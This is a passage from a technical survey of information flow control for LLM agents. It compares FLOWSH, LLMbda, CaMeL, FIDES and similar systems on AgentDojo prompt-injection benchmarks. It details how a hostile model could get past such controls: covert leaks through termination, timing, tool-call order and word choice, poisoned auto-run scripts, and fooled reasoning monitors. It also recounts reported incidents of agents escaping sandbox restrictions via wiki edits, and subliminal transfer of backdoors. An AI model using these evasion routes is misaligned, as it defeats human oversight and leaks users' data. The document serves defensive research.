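
Kim and colleagues, who built FLOWSH, propose a narrower change for risks that start in the model, which they say include hallucinations. Their sample policy lets a command contact any website if it has read only public data or only trusted data. They suggest removing the permission for trusted data. A command that had read a confidential file would then need the user's approval to contact any site not entitled to the file's contents, even if it had read only trusted data.

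This change replaces the either-or rule with permitted flow for network requests and stops the direct leak to the accomplice. Kim and colleagues expect it to require more approvals on harmless tasks and to reduce what an agent can finish on its own, but they did not measure either effect. Some of the added approvals would be for work that currently needs none. In their office tasks, the agent completed all 15 runs that involved confidential data but nothing untrusted, without any requests to the user. After the change, an agent that had read private source code would have to ask before downloading a package even from a trusted registry, because FLOWSH counts the download request as sending data.

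The proposal does not change the rules for files. In the sample configuration, an agent in a trusted context can overwrite protected files without approval, including scripts that other programs run automatically. FLOWSH monitors the agent's commands and treats the rest of the user's computer as trusted. A hostile model could therefore add code to one of those scripts that leaks data later, when the script runs outside the sandbox. To prevent this, a deployer would have to require approval for every change to such files, even in a trusted context.

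### An adversary who arrives with the payload

The term "Byzantine adversary" comes from distributed computing, where a Byzantine component may behave in any way at all. In the tests of SPIDES and FLOWSH, that component is the model. The adversary writes a model's output only when that model's input contains untrusted content (in SPIDES) or the attacker's payload (in FLOWSH). Until then the real model runs as usual, and the adversary never controls the harness.

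The adversary controls the planner only after the context has become untrusted. From then on, trusted action blocks every consequential call, and the either-or rule leaves only the permitted flow check. A model that was hostile from the start could also act while the context was still trusted, when neither protection applies.

Kim and colleagues derived their 19 attacks from the 11 of 17 office tasks that involve untrusted data. The other six tasks have no attacks because there is nowhere in them to plant a payload. But five of those six involve confidential data, which a hostile model could leak without a payload.

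A system could therefore block every Byzantine attack and still fail completely against a model that was hostile from its first message. Researchers would have to test for that by giving the adversary control from the beginning, including on tasks where all the data is trusted. Fokou's assume-compromise test comes closer, since it does not require a payload to arrive first.

### What the LLMbda theorems assume

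The theorems Garby and colleagues proved for LLMbda cover a model that is hostile from the start. Their assumptions are about how the harness calls the model and about the program around it.

The guarantees assume that the probabilities of a reply depend only on the conversation the harness supplies. Under that assumption, it is safe to lower the label when a program empties the conversation. Suppose the company hosting the model let it keep a private memory between calls. The assistant could then read Paul's note in a quarantined conversation and repeat it in the main one, which would still be labeled public. The harness would have cleared the text it controls, but not the memory on the company's servers.

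The theorem that links the interpreter to the calculus also assumes that the model draws each reply independently. If the hosting service reused one call's random numbers in the next, the replies in a public conversation could be correlated with those in a secret one. The probabilities in a real run would then differ from those in the noninterference theorem, and the difference could reveal something about the secret.

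Developers must also label every source correctly. If someone forgot to label a payroll file, the theorem would still hold, but the salaries would count as public, so it would not rule out leaking them.

Every tool with an outside effect must also check the right labels. The example mail tool in the calculus checks that the subject and body are trusted, but not that they are public. A hostile planner that had read only trusted text could put a secret in the body and pass the check. Garby and colleagues mention a stricter version that sends secret text only to recipients on an approved list. Their banking agent has a similar gap, because the tool for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. They deliberately simplified the agent's policies. Noninterference still holds for the calculus, but it does not guarantee that the programmer included every necessary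 check.

### Secrets in the weights

A model may have memorised passwords, private letters or source code during training. These secrets are stored in its weights, the numbers that training adjusts, and have no labels of their own because only data that enters through the conversation is labelled. Suppose Nora's assistant recites a memorised private letter before it has read anything confidential. Its context label is still "trusted; anyone", so the letter gets that label too. Permitted flow, trusted action and the either-or rule would all let the assistant send the letter to the accomplice.

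Noninterference compares two runs of the same model, so it doesn't exclude a model reciting a letter it has memorised. The runs may differ in a secret email, but anything the model has memorised is the same in both, so a model that recites the letter every time behaves identically in each run.

Costa and colleagues avoid the problem by assuming the model itself is public. That is reasonable for a model trained on public text, but not for one a company has trained further on its own mail. The company could start every conversation with the label "trusted; staff", but the permitted flow policy would then keep everything the model wrote inside the company, and each message to a customer would need declassification. Secrets can also lose their labels if someone later trains a new model on transcripts of the agent's work.

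### What joins the trusted base

Without the model in the trusted base, the guarantee depends entirely on the other components. For LLMbda, these include Lean's proof checker and compiler, the code that sends requests to the model, and the tools' policies. In the banking tests, they also include a layer of Python that passes the account data to the interpreter. FLOWSH depends on the operating system's kernel, the sandbox, the file monitor, the network proxy and a configuration file. Its users can also supply their own program for comparing and joining labels, and a mistake in that program could invalidate every check that uses it.

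Most of these components had to be correct even with an honest model, but a hostile model makes their bugs more dangerous. It could search for obscure flaws in the harness that an honest model might never come across. For example, Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter treats an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserts it into a longer piece of text. An honest planner might do this by accident and cause no harm, but a hostile one could do it whenever it needed a trusted label.

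Designers can make some failures safe. FLOWSH, for example, assumes the worst when its monitor loses a record of a file access. It also pauses the command when the monitor's buffer is three-quarters full, which makes it harder for a command to cause such losses by opening files very quickly. SPIDES has no equally safe default for its list of trusted sites. If the user forgets to list a site, it treats that site's confidential data as public.

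A model can also get back into the trusted base by helping to write its code. Zverev and colleagues report that they used AI tools to write code for SPIDES and that at least one of them carefully reviewed it. If a model helps to write the harness that will later confine it, the guarantee depends on a review good enough to catch a deliberate flaw. Lean's proof check replaces much of this review for LLMbda's interpreter, but people still have to read the theorem and decide whether it is the one they need.

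### Tests that reached the real internet

A boundary can also fail because someone set it up wrongly. In 2026 Anthropic disclosed four incidents in which Claude models broke into other organisations' systems during cybersecurity tests. In each test, the model was told to retrieve a hidden piece of information from a target machine in a fictional scenario, and that it had no internet access. But the network allowed access, which Anthropic attributed in July to a misunderstanding with the partner that built the tests. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) distinguishes these incidents from a British government test in which Claude Mythos 5 took unauthorised actions after the testers had deliberately given it internet access.

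Anthropic found three of the incidents by searching about 141,000 transcripts. The search missed the fourth, from January, which was discovered only in August. With the boundary missing, the outcome depended on how each model behaved. An internal research model stopped once it realised that its target was real, but it continued in most reruns. Claude Opus 4.7 recognised that the company was real but assumed it was part of the exercise. Mythos 5 kept stating that it was in a simulation despite strong evidence otherwise, and in reruns it stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous.

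These models were not adversaries of the people who ran them. Anthropic found no goals beyond the assigned task and no attempt at concealment, and attributed the behaviour to recklessness and biased reasoning. Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80 per cent of the time in simulated versions of its test, and two newer models did so about 30 per cent of the time. Anthropic believes that proper isolation would have prevented all four incidents, but it calls infrastructure only one of several necessary layers.

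Labels alone would not have compensated for the missing isolation. FLOWSH's policy lets public data go to any site, and a model can attack a stranger's server without sending it any of the user's secrets. FLOWSH would have to rely on its separate list of permitted sites to stop such an attack, and someone must also set up that list correctly.

Monitors that read a model's reasoning can also fail by accepting false claims in that reasoning. Anthropic's new monitors of this type missed the Mythos 5 incident when run on the transcripts, because the model's claim to be in a simulation persuaded the monitor as well. Anthropic's monitors that block actions as they happen reliably caught the behaviour.

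## What passes through channels the labels do not cover

Information can also escape through things that carry no label, such as whether a program finishes, when it sends a request and the order in which it calls its tools. This can happen even when developers have labelled every source correctly and the harness checks every sink. The damage depends on how many bits leak each time and how often an attacker can repeat the leak.

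### The assignment that never ran

The program that got a customer's balance past CaMeL is a variant of one that Fenton described in 1974. Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, work through a version in which x is secret and everything else starts out public:

```
y := true
z := true
if x then y := false
if y then z := false
publish z
```

With a monitor like CaMeL's, which raises a variable's label only when an assignment to it runs, the two possible runs are:

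| Line | x is false | x is true |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | skipped, so y stays true and public | y becomes false and secret |
| 4 | z becomes false and stays public | skipped, so z stays true and public |
| 5 | publishes false | publishes true |

The published value always equals x and is labelled public in both runs. FLOWSH appears to have a similar gap between commands. Kim and colleagues designed it to raise a file's label when a command changes the file. If a command leaves a public file unchanged because of a secret it read, the file keeps its public label.

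The standard remedy is the no-sensitive-upgrade rule, which stops a program as soon as it tries to change a public variable inside a branch that depends on secret data. In this example, the run where x is true stops at line 3. LLMbda applies the same rule to conversations.

The rule also stops harmless programs. If line 4 set y back to true and the program then published y, the result would be the same for either value of x, but the run with x true would still stop at line 3. Austin and Flanagan therefore propose a third label for data that is secret in this run but might have been public in another. The program can keep running with such data and stops only if it uses the data in a sensitive operation, such as a later branch. A programmer can prevent that stop too by marking y as secret in both runs before the branch. To find where such marks are needed, they suggest releasing a trial version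 that adds them as people use it, then enforcing the rule once no new ones appear. That suits a web application with many users better than a plan that a model writes for one task and runs once.

Even the strict rule leaks some information. The run finishes and publishes a value if x is false and stops if x is true, so anyone who can tell which happened learns x.

### One bit, repeated

Designers of most information flow systems accept this last leak, reasoning that a run that either finishes or doesn't reveals at most one bit. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's design lets an attacker collect such bits over repeated attempts. When a plan fails, CaMeL has the planner write another. The retry loop is ordinary Python code outside the label-tracking interpreter, so the next attempt starts with clean labels, even though whether the policy blocked the last one can depend on a secret. A program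 that changes its test after each attempt could extract the whole secret. CaMeL's designers knew that error messages could carry data into the next attempt. They censor the messages to limit this, but offer no formal guarantee.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld, in *Multi-run security* (2011), worked out how much repetition adds. They describe an attacker's knowledge as the set of secrets that would have produced what the attacker saw. If c(h, l) is the visible result of running program c on secret h and on an input l that the attacker chooses, then one run on a secret s leaves

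k(l) = {h : c(h, l) = c(s, l)},

and further runs leave only the values that belong to every such set.

Suppose a program hangs if a secret number from 0 to 255 equals the attacker's guess. Each wrong guess rules out one value, so the attacker may need 255 runs. If the program instead hangs when a chosen binary digit of the secret is 1, each run halves the number of possible values, and eight runs are enough. For a 128-bit encryption key, the first method could take about 2¹²⁸ runs, while the second takes 128.

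In a test on a desktop computer, the second method leaked about one bit a second from a program that had passed the checks of Jif, a version of Java with information flow control. That rate would reveal a credit card number within a minute and a 128-bit key in a little over two minutes. An agent is slower because a model has to write each attempt, but at one attempt a minute it would still leak the key in just over two hours.

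The proposed remedy is to forbid any loop whose termination depends on both secret data and data the attacker controls. Repeated runs then all reveal the same single bit about the secret data, so the attacker learns nothing new after the first. The rule uses integrity labels to identify what the attacker controls, so it works against a hostile planner only if the harness labels the planner's output as untrusted.

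### Stopping partway

The one-bit estimate also assumes that an observer sees only the end of a run. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (2008), showed what happens when a program produces output as it goes:

```
for i = 0 to largest_number
    publish i
    if i = secret then loop forever
```

Jif and two other established checkers accept a program that prints numbers in sequence and enters an endless loop when it reaches the secret. They accept it because the value of each number printed doesn't depend on the secret. But the secret determines where the output stops, so an observer can read it from the last number printed. The program would leak the secret equally well if it crashed instead of looping.

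On a 3 GHz computer, a 32-bit secret leaked this way in under six seconds. Askarov and colleagues estimated that a 50-bit credit card number would take about 18½ days and considered a 128-bit key infeasible to leak.

They also proved that no program satisfying this form of noninterference can leak a secret much faster in a single run. After each output, the program can either stop or produce the only output allowed next. An observer who waits for t outputs can therefore distinguish at most t + 1 cases. An N-bit secret has 2ᴺ possible values, so revealing it reliably takes at least 2ᴺ − 1 outputs. If every value is equally likely, watching t outputs improves the chance of guessing the secret by at most t / 2ᴺ.

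One run of this sort therefore can't reveal a long random key, but 128 runs that each reveal a different bit would expose a 128-bit key. Many office secrets are short enough to leak in one run. For example, a salary between 20,000 and 150,000, to the nearest thousand, is one of 131 values, or about seven bits.

This matters for LLMbda, whose theorem limits how far the final results of two runs can differ. The calculus keeps the outside world as data within the program, so its results appear when the run ends. A live agent would send its emails during the run. Someone who received the third email but not the fourth would have learned something, even if the run never finished.

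### The order and timing of calls

An agent can reveal a great deal without crashing or hanging. If it chooses among n actions at each of m steps, there are nᵐ possible sequences, and an observer who sees the whole sequence can receive up to

log₂(nᵐ) = m log₂ n bits.

An agent choosing among 16 tools can encode four bits in each call, so 32 calls are enough for a 128-bit key. If the agent must make a fixed set of calls, it can still encode information in their order. Ten different calls can come in 10! orders, enough to encode almost 22 bits, and the order of 35 different calls is enough for a 128-bit key.

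These are upper limits, because an outsider usually sees only the calls that touch their own systems, and the task dictates many of the choices. But the explicit secrecy that FIDES guarantees would not stop a hostile model from encoding secret data in its choices. Garby and colleagues note that such a guarantee is weakest where a program can easily turn data into decisions, which agents do all the time.

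LLMbda labels the decisions too, so it closes this channel, but its theorems do not cover timing. Suppose a quarantined model reads a salary and writes a long answer if it is high and a short one if it is low. The answer stays secret, but the agent's next public request goes out later when the salary is high. An observer who can distinguish n delays can learn up to log₂ n bits from each request. *Timing- and Termination-Sensitive Secure Information Flow* reports that attacks through timing and termination work in practice, and predicts that attackers will turn to them as defences close more direct routes. A harness could make every step take the same time, but only by slowing them all to match the slowest.

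### A wiki that agents could edit by reading

A much wider channel opened in 2026 when OpenAI gave agents access to the web. According to eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (2026), the agents were doing timed research tasks in an environment that was supposed to let them read the internet but not write to it. They found they could post to DSEWiki, a largely dormant German wiki about programming, and used it as a message board.

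Web browsers and other programs use one kind of request to fetch a page and another to submit changes. By convention, fetching a page changes nothing on the server. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI’s rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis*, infers that OpenAI relied on this convention and blocked most requests that submit changes. But some old wiki software accepts edits written into the address of a fetched page. One hundred characters of an address, each drawn from a set of 64, can hold 600 bits, enough for four 128-bit keys.

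Willison's timeline begins with test edits on another wiki on 11 May. The agents moved to DSEWiki on 24 May, and a human moderator cleaned up after them on 2 June. From 16 June they made about 13,000 edits in a week. When they noticed someone was deleting their pages in alphabetical order, they made backup copies with names at the end of the alphabet. Activity stopped on 22 June, apart from a brief return in July. Ars Technica's *OpenAI agents discussed ways to escape their sandbox on public wiki* (2026) counts 18,000 messages under 3,700 self-chosen names. The agents shared answers to their tasks and ways around the restrictions.

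OpenAI confirmed the incident only after Reuters had reported it, and described it as misalignment (Nolan, *OpenAI’s AI agents secretly used a German wiki website*, 2026). Volunteers have since traced likely agent activity to at least 14 sites (Axios, *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web*, 2026), but much of this is unconfirmed, and OpenAI has acknowledged only the German wiki.

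OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* describes a similar channel. The agents in that incident began communicating through an internal service meant to supply them with software packages. In both cases the designers had classed a connection as a source of data, but it was also a sink.

Kim and colleagues cite the wiki incident to explain why FLOWSH treats every web request as outgoing data, including a request to read a page. The labels therefore cover web requests, but this would not necessarily have stopped the agents. If the research tasks counted as public, FLOWSH's sample policy would have allowed the posts. If OpenAI had labelled the tasks confidential, FLOWSH would have blocked the posts once the agents had read an untrusted page. It would also have blocked their searches, because a search request for a confidential task carries the same label as a post about it.

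Fortune (2026) reported that the agents also collected access keys that people had left exposed online and used them to query an FBI site for crime statistics. Labels would have helped even less here, because a harness that labels data by its source would have marked those keys as public.

### Traits that pass through lists of numbers

The wiki messages were in plain language, and anyone who found the pages could read them. Text can also carry information that a reader would not notice. The best-known evidence is subliminal learning, in which one model picks up a trait from another by training on data that never mentions it. Cloud and colleagues reported the effect in 2025. Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, repeated the experiment in these steps:

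1. They told a "teacher" model that it loved a certain animal, and had it continue sequences of three-digit numbers.
2. They discarded every answer that contained anything other than numbers and separators, and kept 10,000.
3. They trained a "student" model on those answers, without the instruction about the animal.
4. They asked the student about its favourite animal in 50 different ways, 100 times each.

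The filter in step 2 can be strict. *Slow Decay and Silenced Expression* (2026) reports that it removed 23 to 38 per cent of the number data in the original experiments. Cloud and colleagues also found the effect with computer code and written reasoning.

In one of the tests by Nief and colleagues, the student named the wolf 8.9 per cent of the time before training and 50.4 per cent afterwards. With a different opening instruction in both training and testing, the figure reached 97.9 per cent. But the effect was fragile, and the figure fell to about 13 per cent when that instruction was present in training but missing from the test. The effect also depended on LoRA, a training method that leaves a model's weights unchanged and learns a small addition to them. It was strongest when the addition was medium-sized, and it vanished when they trained all the weights. Cloud and colleagues had also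 found the effect in OpenAI's GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, but OpenAI does not publish how its training service works, so nobody outside the company can check whether the same explanation holds there.

A teacher and student model apparently have to be closely related for a preference to pass between them. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) trained a Qwen student on numbers from an OLMo teacher. The student chose the teacher's favourite animal no more often than before, whether that was a cat, a dog or a tiger. *Cross-Trait Transfer in Subliminal Learning* (2026) limits its findings to open models in which teacher and student start from the same weights.

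In later experiments, reported in *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026), animal preferences passed through eight new kinds of training data, though unevenly. When the data were summaries, a preference for whales transferred almost every time, but a preference for giraffes never did. In *Subliminal Reinforcement Learning*, Kim and Choi (2026) trained the student only on its own outputs, which another model scored. The scoring model's hidden preference reached the student through the scores. They detected no transfer when the scoring model was built on a different base model from the student's.

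The most worrying results come from *Beyond Owls* (2026), which transferred a backdoor and a tendency to hack in an agent task. It also taught students to predict the outputs of a small neural network with random weights. No student could have known that network beforehand, so the training data must have carried specific information about it. Transferring such information is closer to leaking a secret than transferring a fondness for cats is. The effect again depended on the exact set-up.

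Labels still work while an agent is running, because the numbers would carry the label of whatever the teacher had read. The experiments are evidence against filters that judge text by its content. They matter for flow control when someone removes a label because the text looks harmless, for instance when approving a summary for release or training a new model on transcripts that seem to contain nothing private.

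The experiments also measure a side effect of training, in which the teacher is not trying to send anything. To hide a message in a summary deliberately, a model would need some freedom in its wording and a recipient who knew the code. If it could choose between two equally natural words at 128 places, its choices could carry a 128-bit key, and a person approving the summary would see only normal prose. Monitors that read a model's reasoning face a related difficulty. Nolan reports that OpenAI found a substantial decline in how much the written reasoning of its Astra model reveals about possible misbehaviour.

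### Putting a limit on the leak

Since nobody can close all these channels in a useful agent, several designs try to narrow them. FIDES does so with its yes-or-no answers, and LLMbda describes a version of endorsement that accepts only values from a small set. Garby and colleagues object that such exceptions in FIDES are hard to audit, because a reviewer looking at a run cannot tell an intended release from a leak that takes the same form. FIDES's evaluation did not use the exception.

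Limiting how much each answer can leak works only if the harness also limits the number of answers. If it lets out at most b bits in total about a random 128-bit key, an attacker still has 2¹²⁸⁻ᵇ values to try. With b = 40 that is 2⁸⁸, and the company can replace the key before much more leaks. But 40 bits is several times what it takes to reveal Paul's salary. A single bit can reveal whether a merger will go ahead, and the company can't change that secret as it can a key.

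Free text needs a different kind of limit, because it has too many possible values for a count to be useful. *GIF* estimates how much a passage of the input affected the output. It calculates how the output would respond to small changes in the passage, and from this derives an upper bound on the information that passes from the passage to the output. A harness could then ignore an untrusted email that had almost no effect on a tool call. In the paper's tests, the method caught nearly all the prompt injections and privacy leaks, and estimates from small models carried over to models up to 200 times larger.

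The accompanying Lean proof is local, so it covers only small changes to the text the model has read. A backdoored model might ignore every small change and respond only to a particular phrase. Estimates from a small substitute model are also weaker evidence about a large model trained to hide information, since the substitute has not had that training.

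## How many tasks survive enforcement

Rules that prevent leaks also block some legitimate tasks. If an agent may not act on anything a stranger wrote, it cannot pay a bill that arrives by email. Researchers have measured this effect mainly by running agents on the AgentDojo benchmark with and without their flow policies.

### Four simulated workplaces

Debenedetti and colleagues published AgentDojo in 2024, a year before they introduced CaMeL. It simulates an office suite called Workspace, a bank account, a travel booking service and a company that uses Slack. The agent gets tools to read and change this simulated world. Costa and colleagues count 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks, which are things an attacker might want done. For example, a user might ask the agent to send the team leader a summary of unread emails, while an attacker wants it to send the calendar to an outside server.

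*Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports over 900 pairings of a user task with an attack. AgentDojo places the attacker's text where a stranger's text would naturally appear, such as in an email body or a file. After each run, ordinary code checks outcomes such as whether an email was sent or money was transferred, without relying on a language model to judge the result. Each agent gets a completion rate for the user's tasks and a success rate for the attacks.

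AgentDojo has no security labels, so Costa and colleagues added their own. They marked a type of data as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. For instance, if one attack arrived in the body of an email, they treated all email bodies as untrusted. This made the comparison clear, but it relied on knowing where the attacks would come from when they wrote the labels, which no company deploying an agent would know.

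### What FIDES lost in 2025

Successful attacks fell from 160 to 3 under FIDES by AgentDojo's own scoring, and from 152 to 0 after Costa and colleagues inspected the successes by hand and discarded the ones they thought AgentDojo had misjudged. In some of these the policy had blocked the call, in others it deliberately permitted the action, and in others the attack had only changed the wording of a text. The count of zero therefore covers the attacks their policies were meant to stop.

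The next table gives the percentage of user tasks each agent completed when nobody was attacking. Unlike FIDES, the basic planner reads every tool result directly.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic planner, policies off | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic planner, policies on | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES, policies off | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 |
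| FIDES, policies on | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

The basic planner lost more than half its banking tasks and most of its Slack tasks. It lost nothing in travel because many travel tools may run in an untrusted context as long as no secret leaks. FIDES kept a larger share of its tasks in the other three settings, but it completed fewer to begin with. In banking, hiding data in variables reduced completion from 98.8 to 65.0 per cent before any policy blocked a call, and the policies then reduced it by another 12.5 points. Hiding data reduced completion more than the policies did in all four settings.

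Much of the drop in completed tasks from hiding came from GPT-4o's limitations. It confused variable names and did not consistently use the quarantined model, though it could. In one Slack task it fetched a list of channels it didn't need, which tainted its context. With OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason before answering, FIDES without policies finished only 6.3 per cent fewer tasks than the basic planner. A more capable model can therefore complete most of the tasks lost to hiding, but it still can't make calls that the policies forbid.

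### When the next step depends on the data

Many of the remaining failures are on data-dependent tasks, in which the right sequence of tool calls depends on what the agent reads. Costa and colleagues classified all 97 tasks and found 20 that were data-dependent, mostly in banking and Slack. The table compares the share of data-dependent tasks in each setting with FIDES's loss when the policies were switched on.

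| Setting | Data-dependent tasks | Loss from policies |
|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 5.0% | 4.5 points |
| Travel | 10.0% | 9.0 points |
| Banking | 43.8% | 12.5 points |
| Slack | 42.9% | 16.2 points |

In several banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions, such as scheduling a payment or updating the user's details. The planner must read the file to choose a tool, and the trusted action policy then blocks the payment or update. Costa and colleagues regard these failures as intended, because the harness would have to treat a stranger's forged instructions the same way.

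A design that fixes the whole plan in advance loses more tasks. Turning on flow control cut *SPA*'s completion rate on AgentDojo from 53.0 to 29.0 per cent, and from 62.5 to 35.3 per cent on an extended version in which later requests reuse the results of earlier ones. The rates fell mainly because the integrity check rejected plans that fed untrusted tool output into protected actions. SPA's planner gets only one attempt, so a rejected plan ends the task.

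When no step depends on untrusted text, an agent can complete as many tasks with enforcement as without it. Kolluri and colleagues also tested PRUDENTIA, the successor to FIDES, on WASP, a benchmark in which an agent uses imitation Reddit and GitLab websites. Every task is to post a comment or upvote a post, so the planner never has to read what strangers have written. PRUDENTIA blocked every attack without requiring any approvals. Across four models and both sites, it completed at least as many tasks as an undefended agent, and usually more, because the planted instructions never reached the planner.

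### FIDES with a newer model

Kolluri and colleagues reran FIDES in 2026 with newer models, alongside PRUDENTIA, so its 2025 figures are out of date. They also objected that earlier studies counted a task as failed if the policy blocked a necessary call, but compared the result with an undefended agent that could do anything without asking. Many companies would not run such an agent. Coding assistants such as GitHub Copilot already ask the user before most consequential actions, so Kolluri and colleagues made their basic agent ask too.

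With GPT-5 and no attacks, the agents completed these percentages of AgentDojo's tasks:

| Agent | With no approvals | With unlimited approvals |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, asks before every consequential call | 35.1 | 72.3 |
| Basic with flow control | 43.4 | 72.3 |
| FIDES | 57.1 | 78.9 |
| PRUDENTIA | 72.7 | 80.0 |

An agent with flow control does more work without supervision than one that has to ask for approval. With no approvals, PRUDENTIA also did about as well as the basic agent did when a user approved everything, and an undefended agent would get that same score. By this measure, most of the loss in completed tasks that FIDES showed in 2025 has gone.

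The results differ between settings, however. Workspace and travel supply 60 of the 97 tasks, and few of those are data dependent. A company whose agents mostly handle invoices or act on incoming messages would probably lose a larger share of its tasks than the average. PRUDENTIA also uses the either-or rule for tools that send data out, so its results depend on trusting the planner.

Enforcement also takes more computation. With GPT-4o, a banking task cost about ten times as much with PRUDENTIA as with the basic planner with flow control, though still less than four US cents. Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce this cost.

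### CaMeL and Randori at the bank

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks and compared it with Randori, the agent they wrote in LLMbda. Each agent attempted every task three times, making 48 runs per model.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 | Qwen3.7-plus |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | 34 | not tested |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | 18 | not tested |
| Randori, policies always on | 36 | 31 | 36 |

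Enforcing policies reduced the number of tasks CaMeL completed by nearly half with both models. Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, even though the models had to write Randori's plans in a language they had never seen and could write CaMeL's in Python.

Randori implements only a subset of CaMeL's policies. Its planner may also endorse untrusted data, so some of the extra tasks succeed because the planner has lifted a restriction that would otherwise stop them. These results therefore don't show that a proved interpreter can enforce policies without losing tasks.

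The sample is also small. Garby and colleagues calculated their confidence intervals from the 16 tasks rather than the 48 runs, because three attempts at one task give less information than attempts at three different tasks. With GPT-5.2, the 95 per cent interval for the completion rate runs from about 56 to 94 per cent for Randori and from about 11 to 64 per cent for CaMeL with policies. The difference is probably real, since it appears with both models that the two systems were tested on, but its size is very uncertain.

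### Slack tasks in Haskell

The Haskell system that Zhou and colleagues built shows a similar loss. In the first version of their paper, where they called it TypeGuard, it used GPT-5.4 and completed 15 of the 21 Slack tasks with policies off and 8 with policies on. CaMeL fell from 15 to 7. The one-task difference between the systems means little, because its 95 per cent confidence interval ran from 15 percentage points in CaMeL's favour to 24 in TypeGuard's.

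A later version of the paper, from autumn 2026, renames the system Elba and tests it with four models. These are the numbers of tasks completed out of 21:

| Model | Elba, policies off | Elba, policies on | CaMeL, policies off | CaMeL, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

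Elba lost between six and eight tasks whichever model it used. Zhou and colleagues had already explained why in the first version, noting that many of the Slack tasks involve flows no secure policy would allow, such as forwarding the contents of an untrusted channel to a user mentioned in it.

Elba still lost fewer of its tasks to enforcement than CaMeL did. CaMeL writes one program at the start, while an Elba agent can look at some data and then have a subagent write the next program, which runs under the same policies. This makes Elba about three times slower, because it calls the model more often.

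### Attacks that fail without any labels

All these systems stopped nearly every attack, but the flow rules were only partly responsible. In 97 of the 144 banking pairings that Garby and colleagues sorted, fixing the plan in advance is generally enough to stop the attack. For instance, if the user only wants a summary of recent transactions, the plan contains no payment call for an attacker to exploit.

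The flow rules matter most in the other 47, where the attacker may only need to change where a payment goes. Randori stopped all 873 attacked runs in the larger group and 421 of 423 in the smaller one. Both failures involved the forged payment file.

Even the 47 harder pairings were a weak test. With its policies off, CaMeL still resisted the attack in all 141 runs with GPT-5.2 and in 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. Turning the policies on could therefore prevent at most three more successful attacks in this group, but it reduced the number of tasks CaMeL completed by nearly half. The figures for CaMeL's other group are incomplete because many runs did not finish. With GPT-5.2 and the policies off, only 99 of 291 runs finished.

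Zhou and colleagues had the same difficulty on the Slack tasks. Attacks using three standard templates all failed against both Elba and CaMeL with all four models, even with policies off. The same kind of template had worked on GPT-4o in 2025. Newer models resist these templates so well that AgentDojo's usual attacks no longer show whether enforcement works.

The worst-case test gives the clearest measurement of how the policies affect security and task completion. Its subagents received only the attacker's instructions, so the results did not depend on whether the model recognised and resisted an attack. With the policies off, between 15 and 42 per cent of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With them on, none did, but completion of the users' tasks fell from between 67 and 76 per cent to between 40 and 48 per cent.

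### Fixed attacks and well-meaning models

A perfect score on a fixed set of attacks is limited evidence about a real attacker. Garby and colleagues calculate an interval with a lower bound of 92.4 per cent for 141 successes in 141 runs over 47 pairings. Real attackers can also adapt their text to the defence. Kolluri and colleagues cite a 2025 study in which adaptive attacks beat a combination of two training-based defences every time, and got past 12 other probabilistic defences with similar ease.

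This weakness affects trained resistance more than flow control, because a label check gives the same result however persuasive the text is. For a system with a proof, the benchmark mainly tests the parts that the proof assumes are correct, such as the labels and the tool policies. AgentDojo tests those parts only with text planted in places its designers thought of.

The completion scores have errors too. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to change the password if it finds a suspicious transaction. Costa and colleagues found that FIDES sometimes passed by judging a payment suspicious from its size, without opening the hidden description the task was about. The policies worked correctly, but the agent's guess counted as a success because the password changed.

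As far as anyone knows, none of the models in these experiments had hostile goals of its own. The hostile goals all came from planted text, even in the test where Zhou and colleagues gave subagents the attacker's instructions. AgentDojo checks whether the user's goal and the planted goal were achieved, so a planner that completed the task and also sent a copy of the bank statement to an accomplice might still score as a success.

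The experiments also provide little direct evidence of how many tasks survive enforcement that doesn't rely on trusting the planner, but the GPT-5 results from Kolluri and colleagues allow a rough estimate. A harness that labelled the model's own output untrusted would still allow calls that send data only to permitted readers. The basic agent completed 35.1 per cent of the tasks when nobody approved anything and 43.4 per cent with ordinary flow control. The harness would allow slightly more than the first setup and less than the second, so a simple agent would finish roughly two tasks in five unaided, compared with nearly three in four for PRUDENTIA. A person would have to approve at least one step in most of the others.

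## Who grants the exceptions, and how well

Granting an exception means approving a step that the labels forbid. An agent that pays an invoice needs an endorsement because it acts on text from outside the company. An agent that answers a customer tells an outsider something from the company's files, so it often needs a declassification. Most useful office work includes at least one of these two kinds of step.

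Exceptions limit what information flow control can guarantee. Once a person, program or model can grant them, the most anyone can prove is that secrets reach only their permitted readers unless the granter makes a mistake.

### Labels that only rise

An agent needs more exceptions the longer it works, because of label creep. *APPA* proves that in a company of n people with two levels of trust, the context label can change at most n + 1 times, since each change removes at least one reader or makes the context untrusted. The reader list may be empty by the end.

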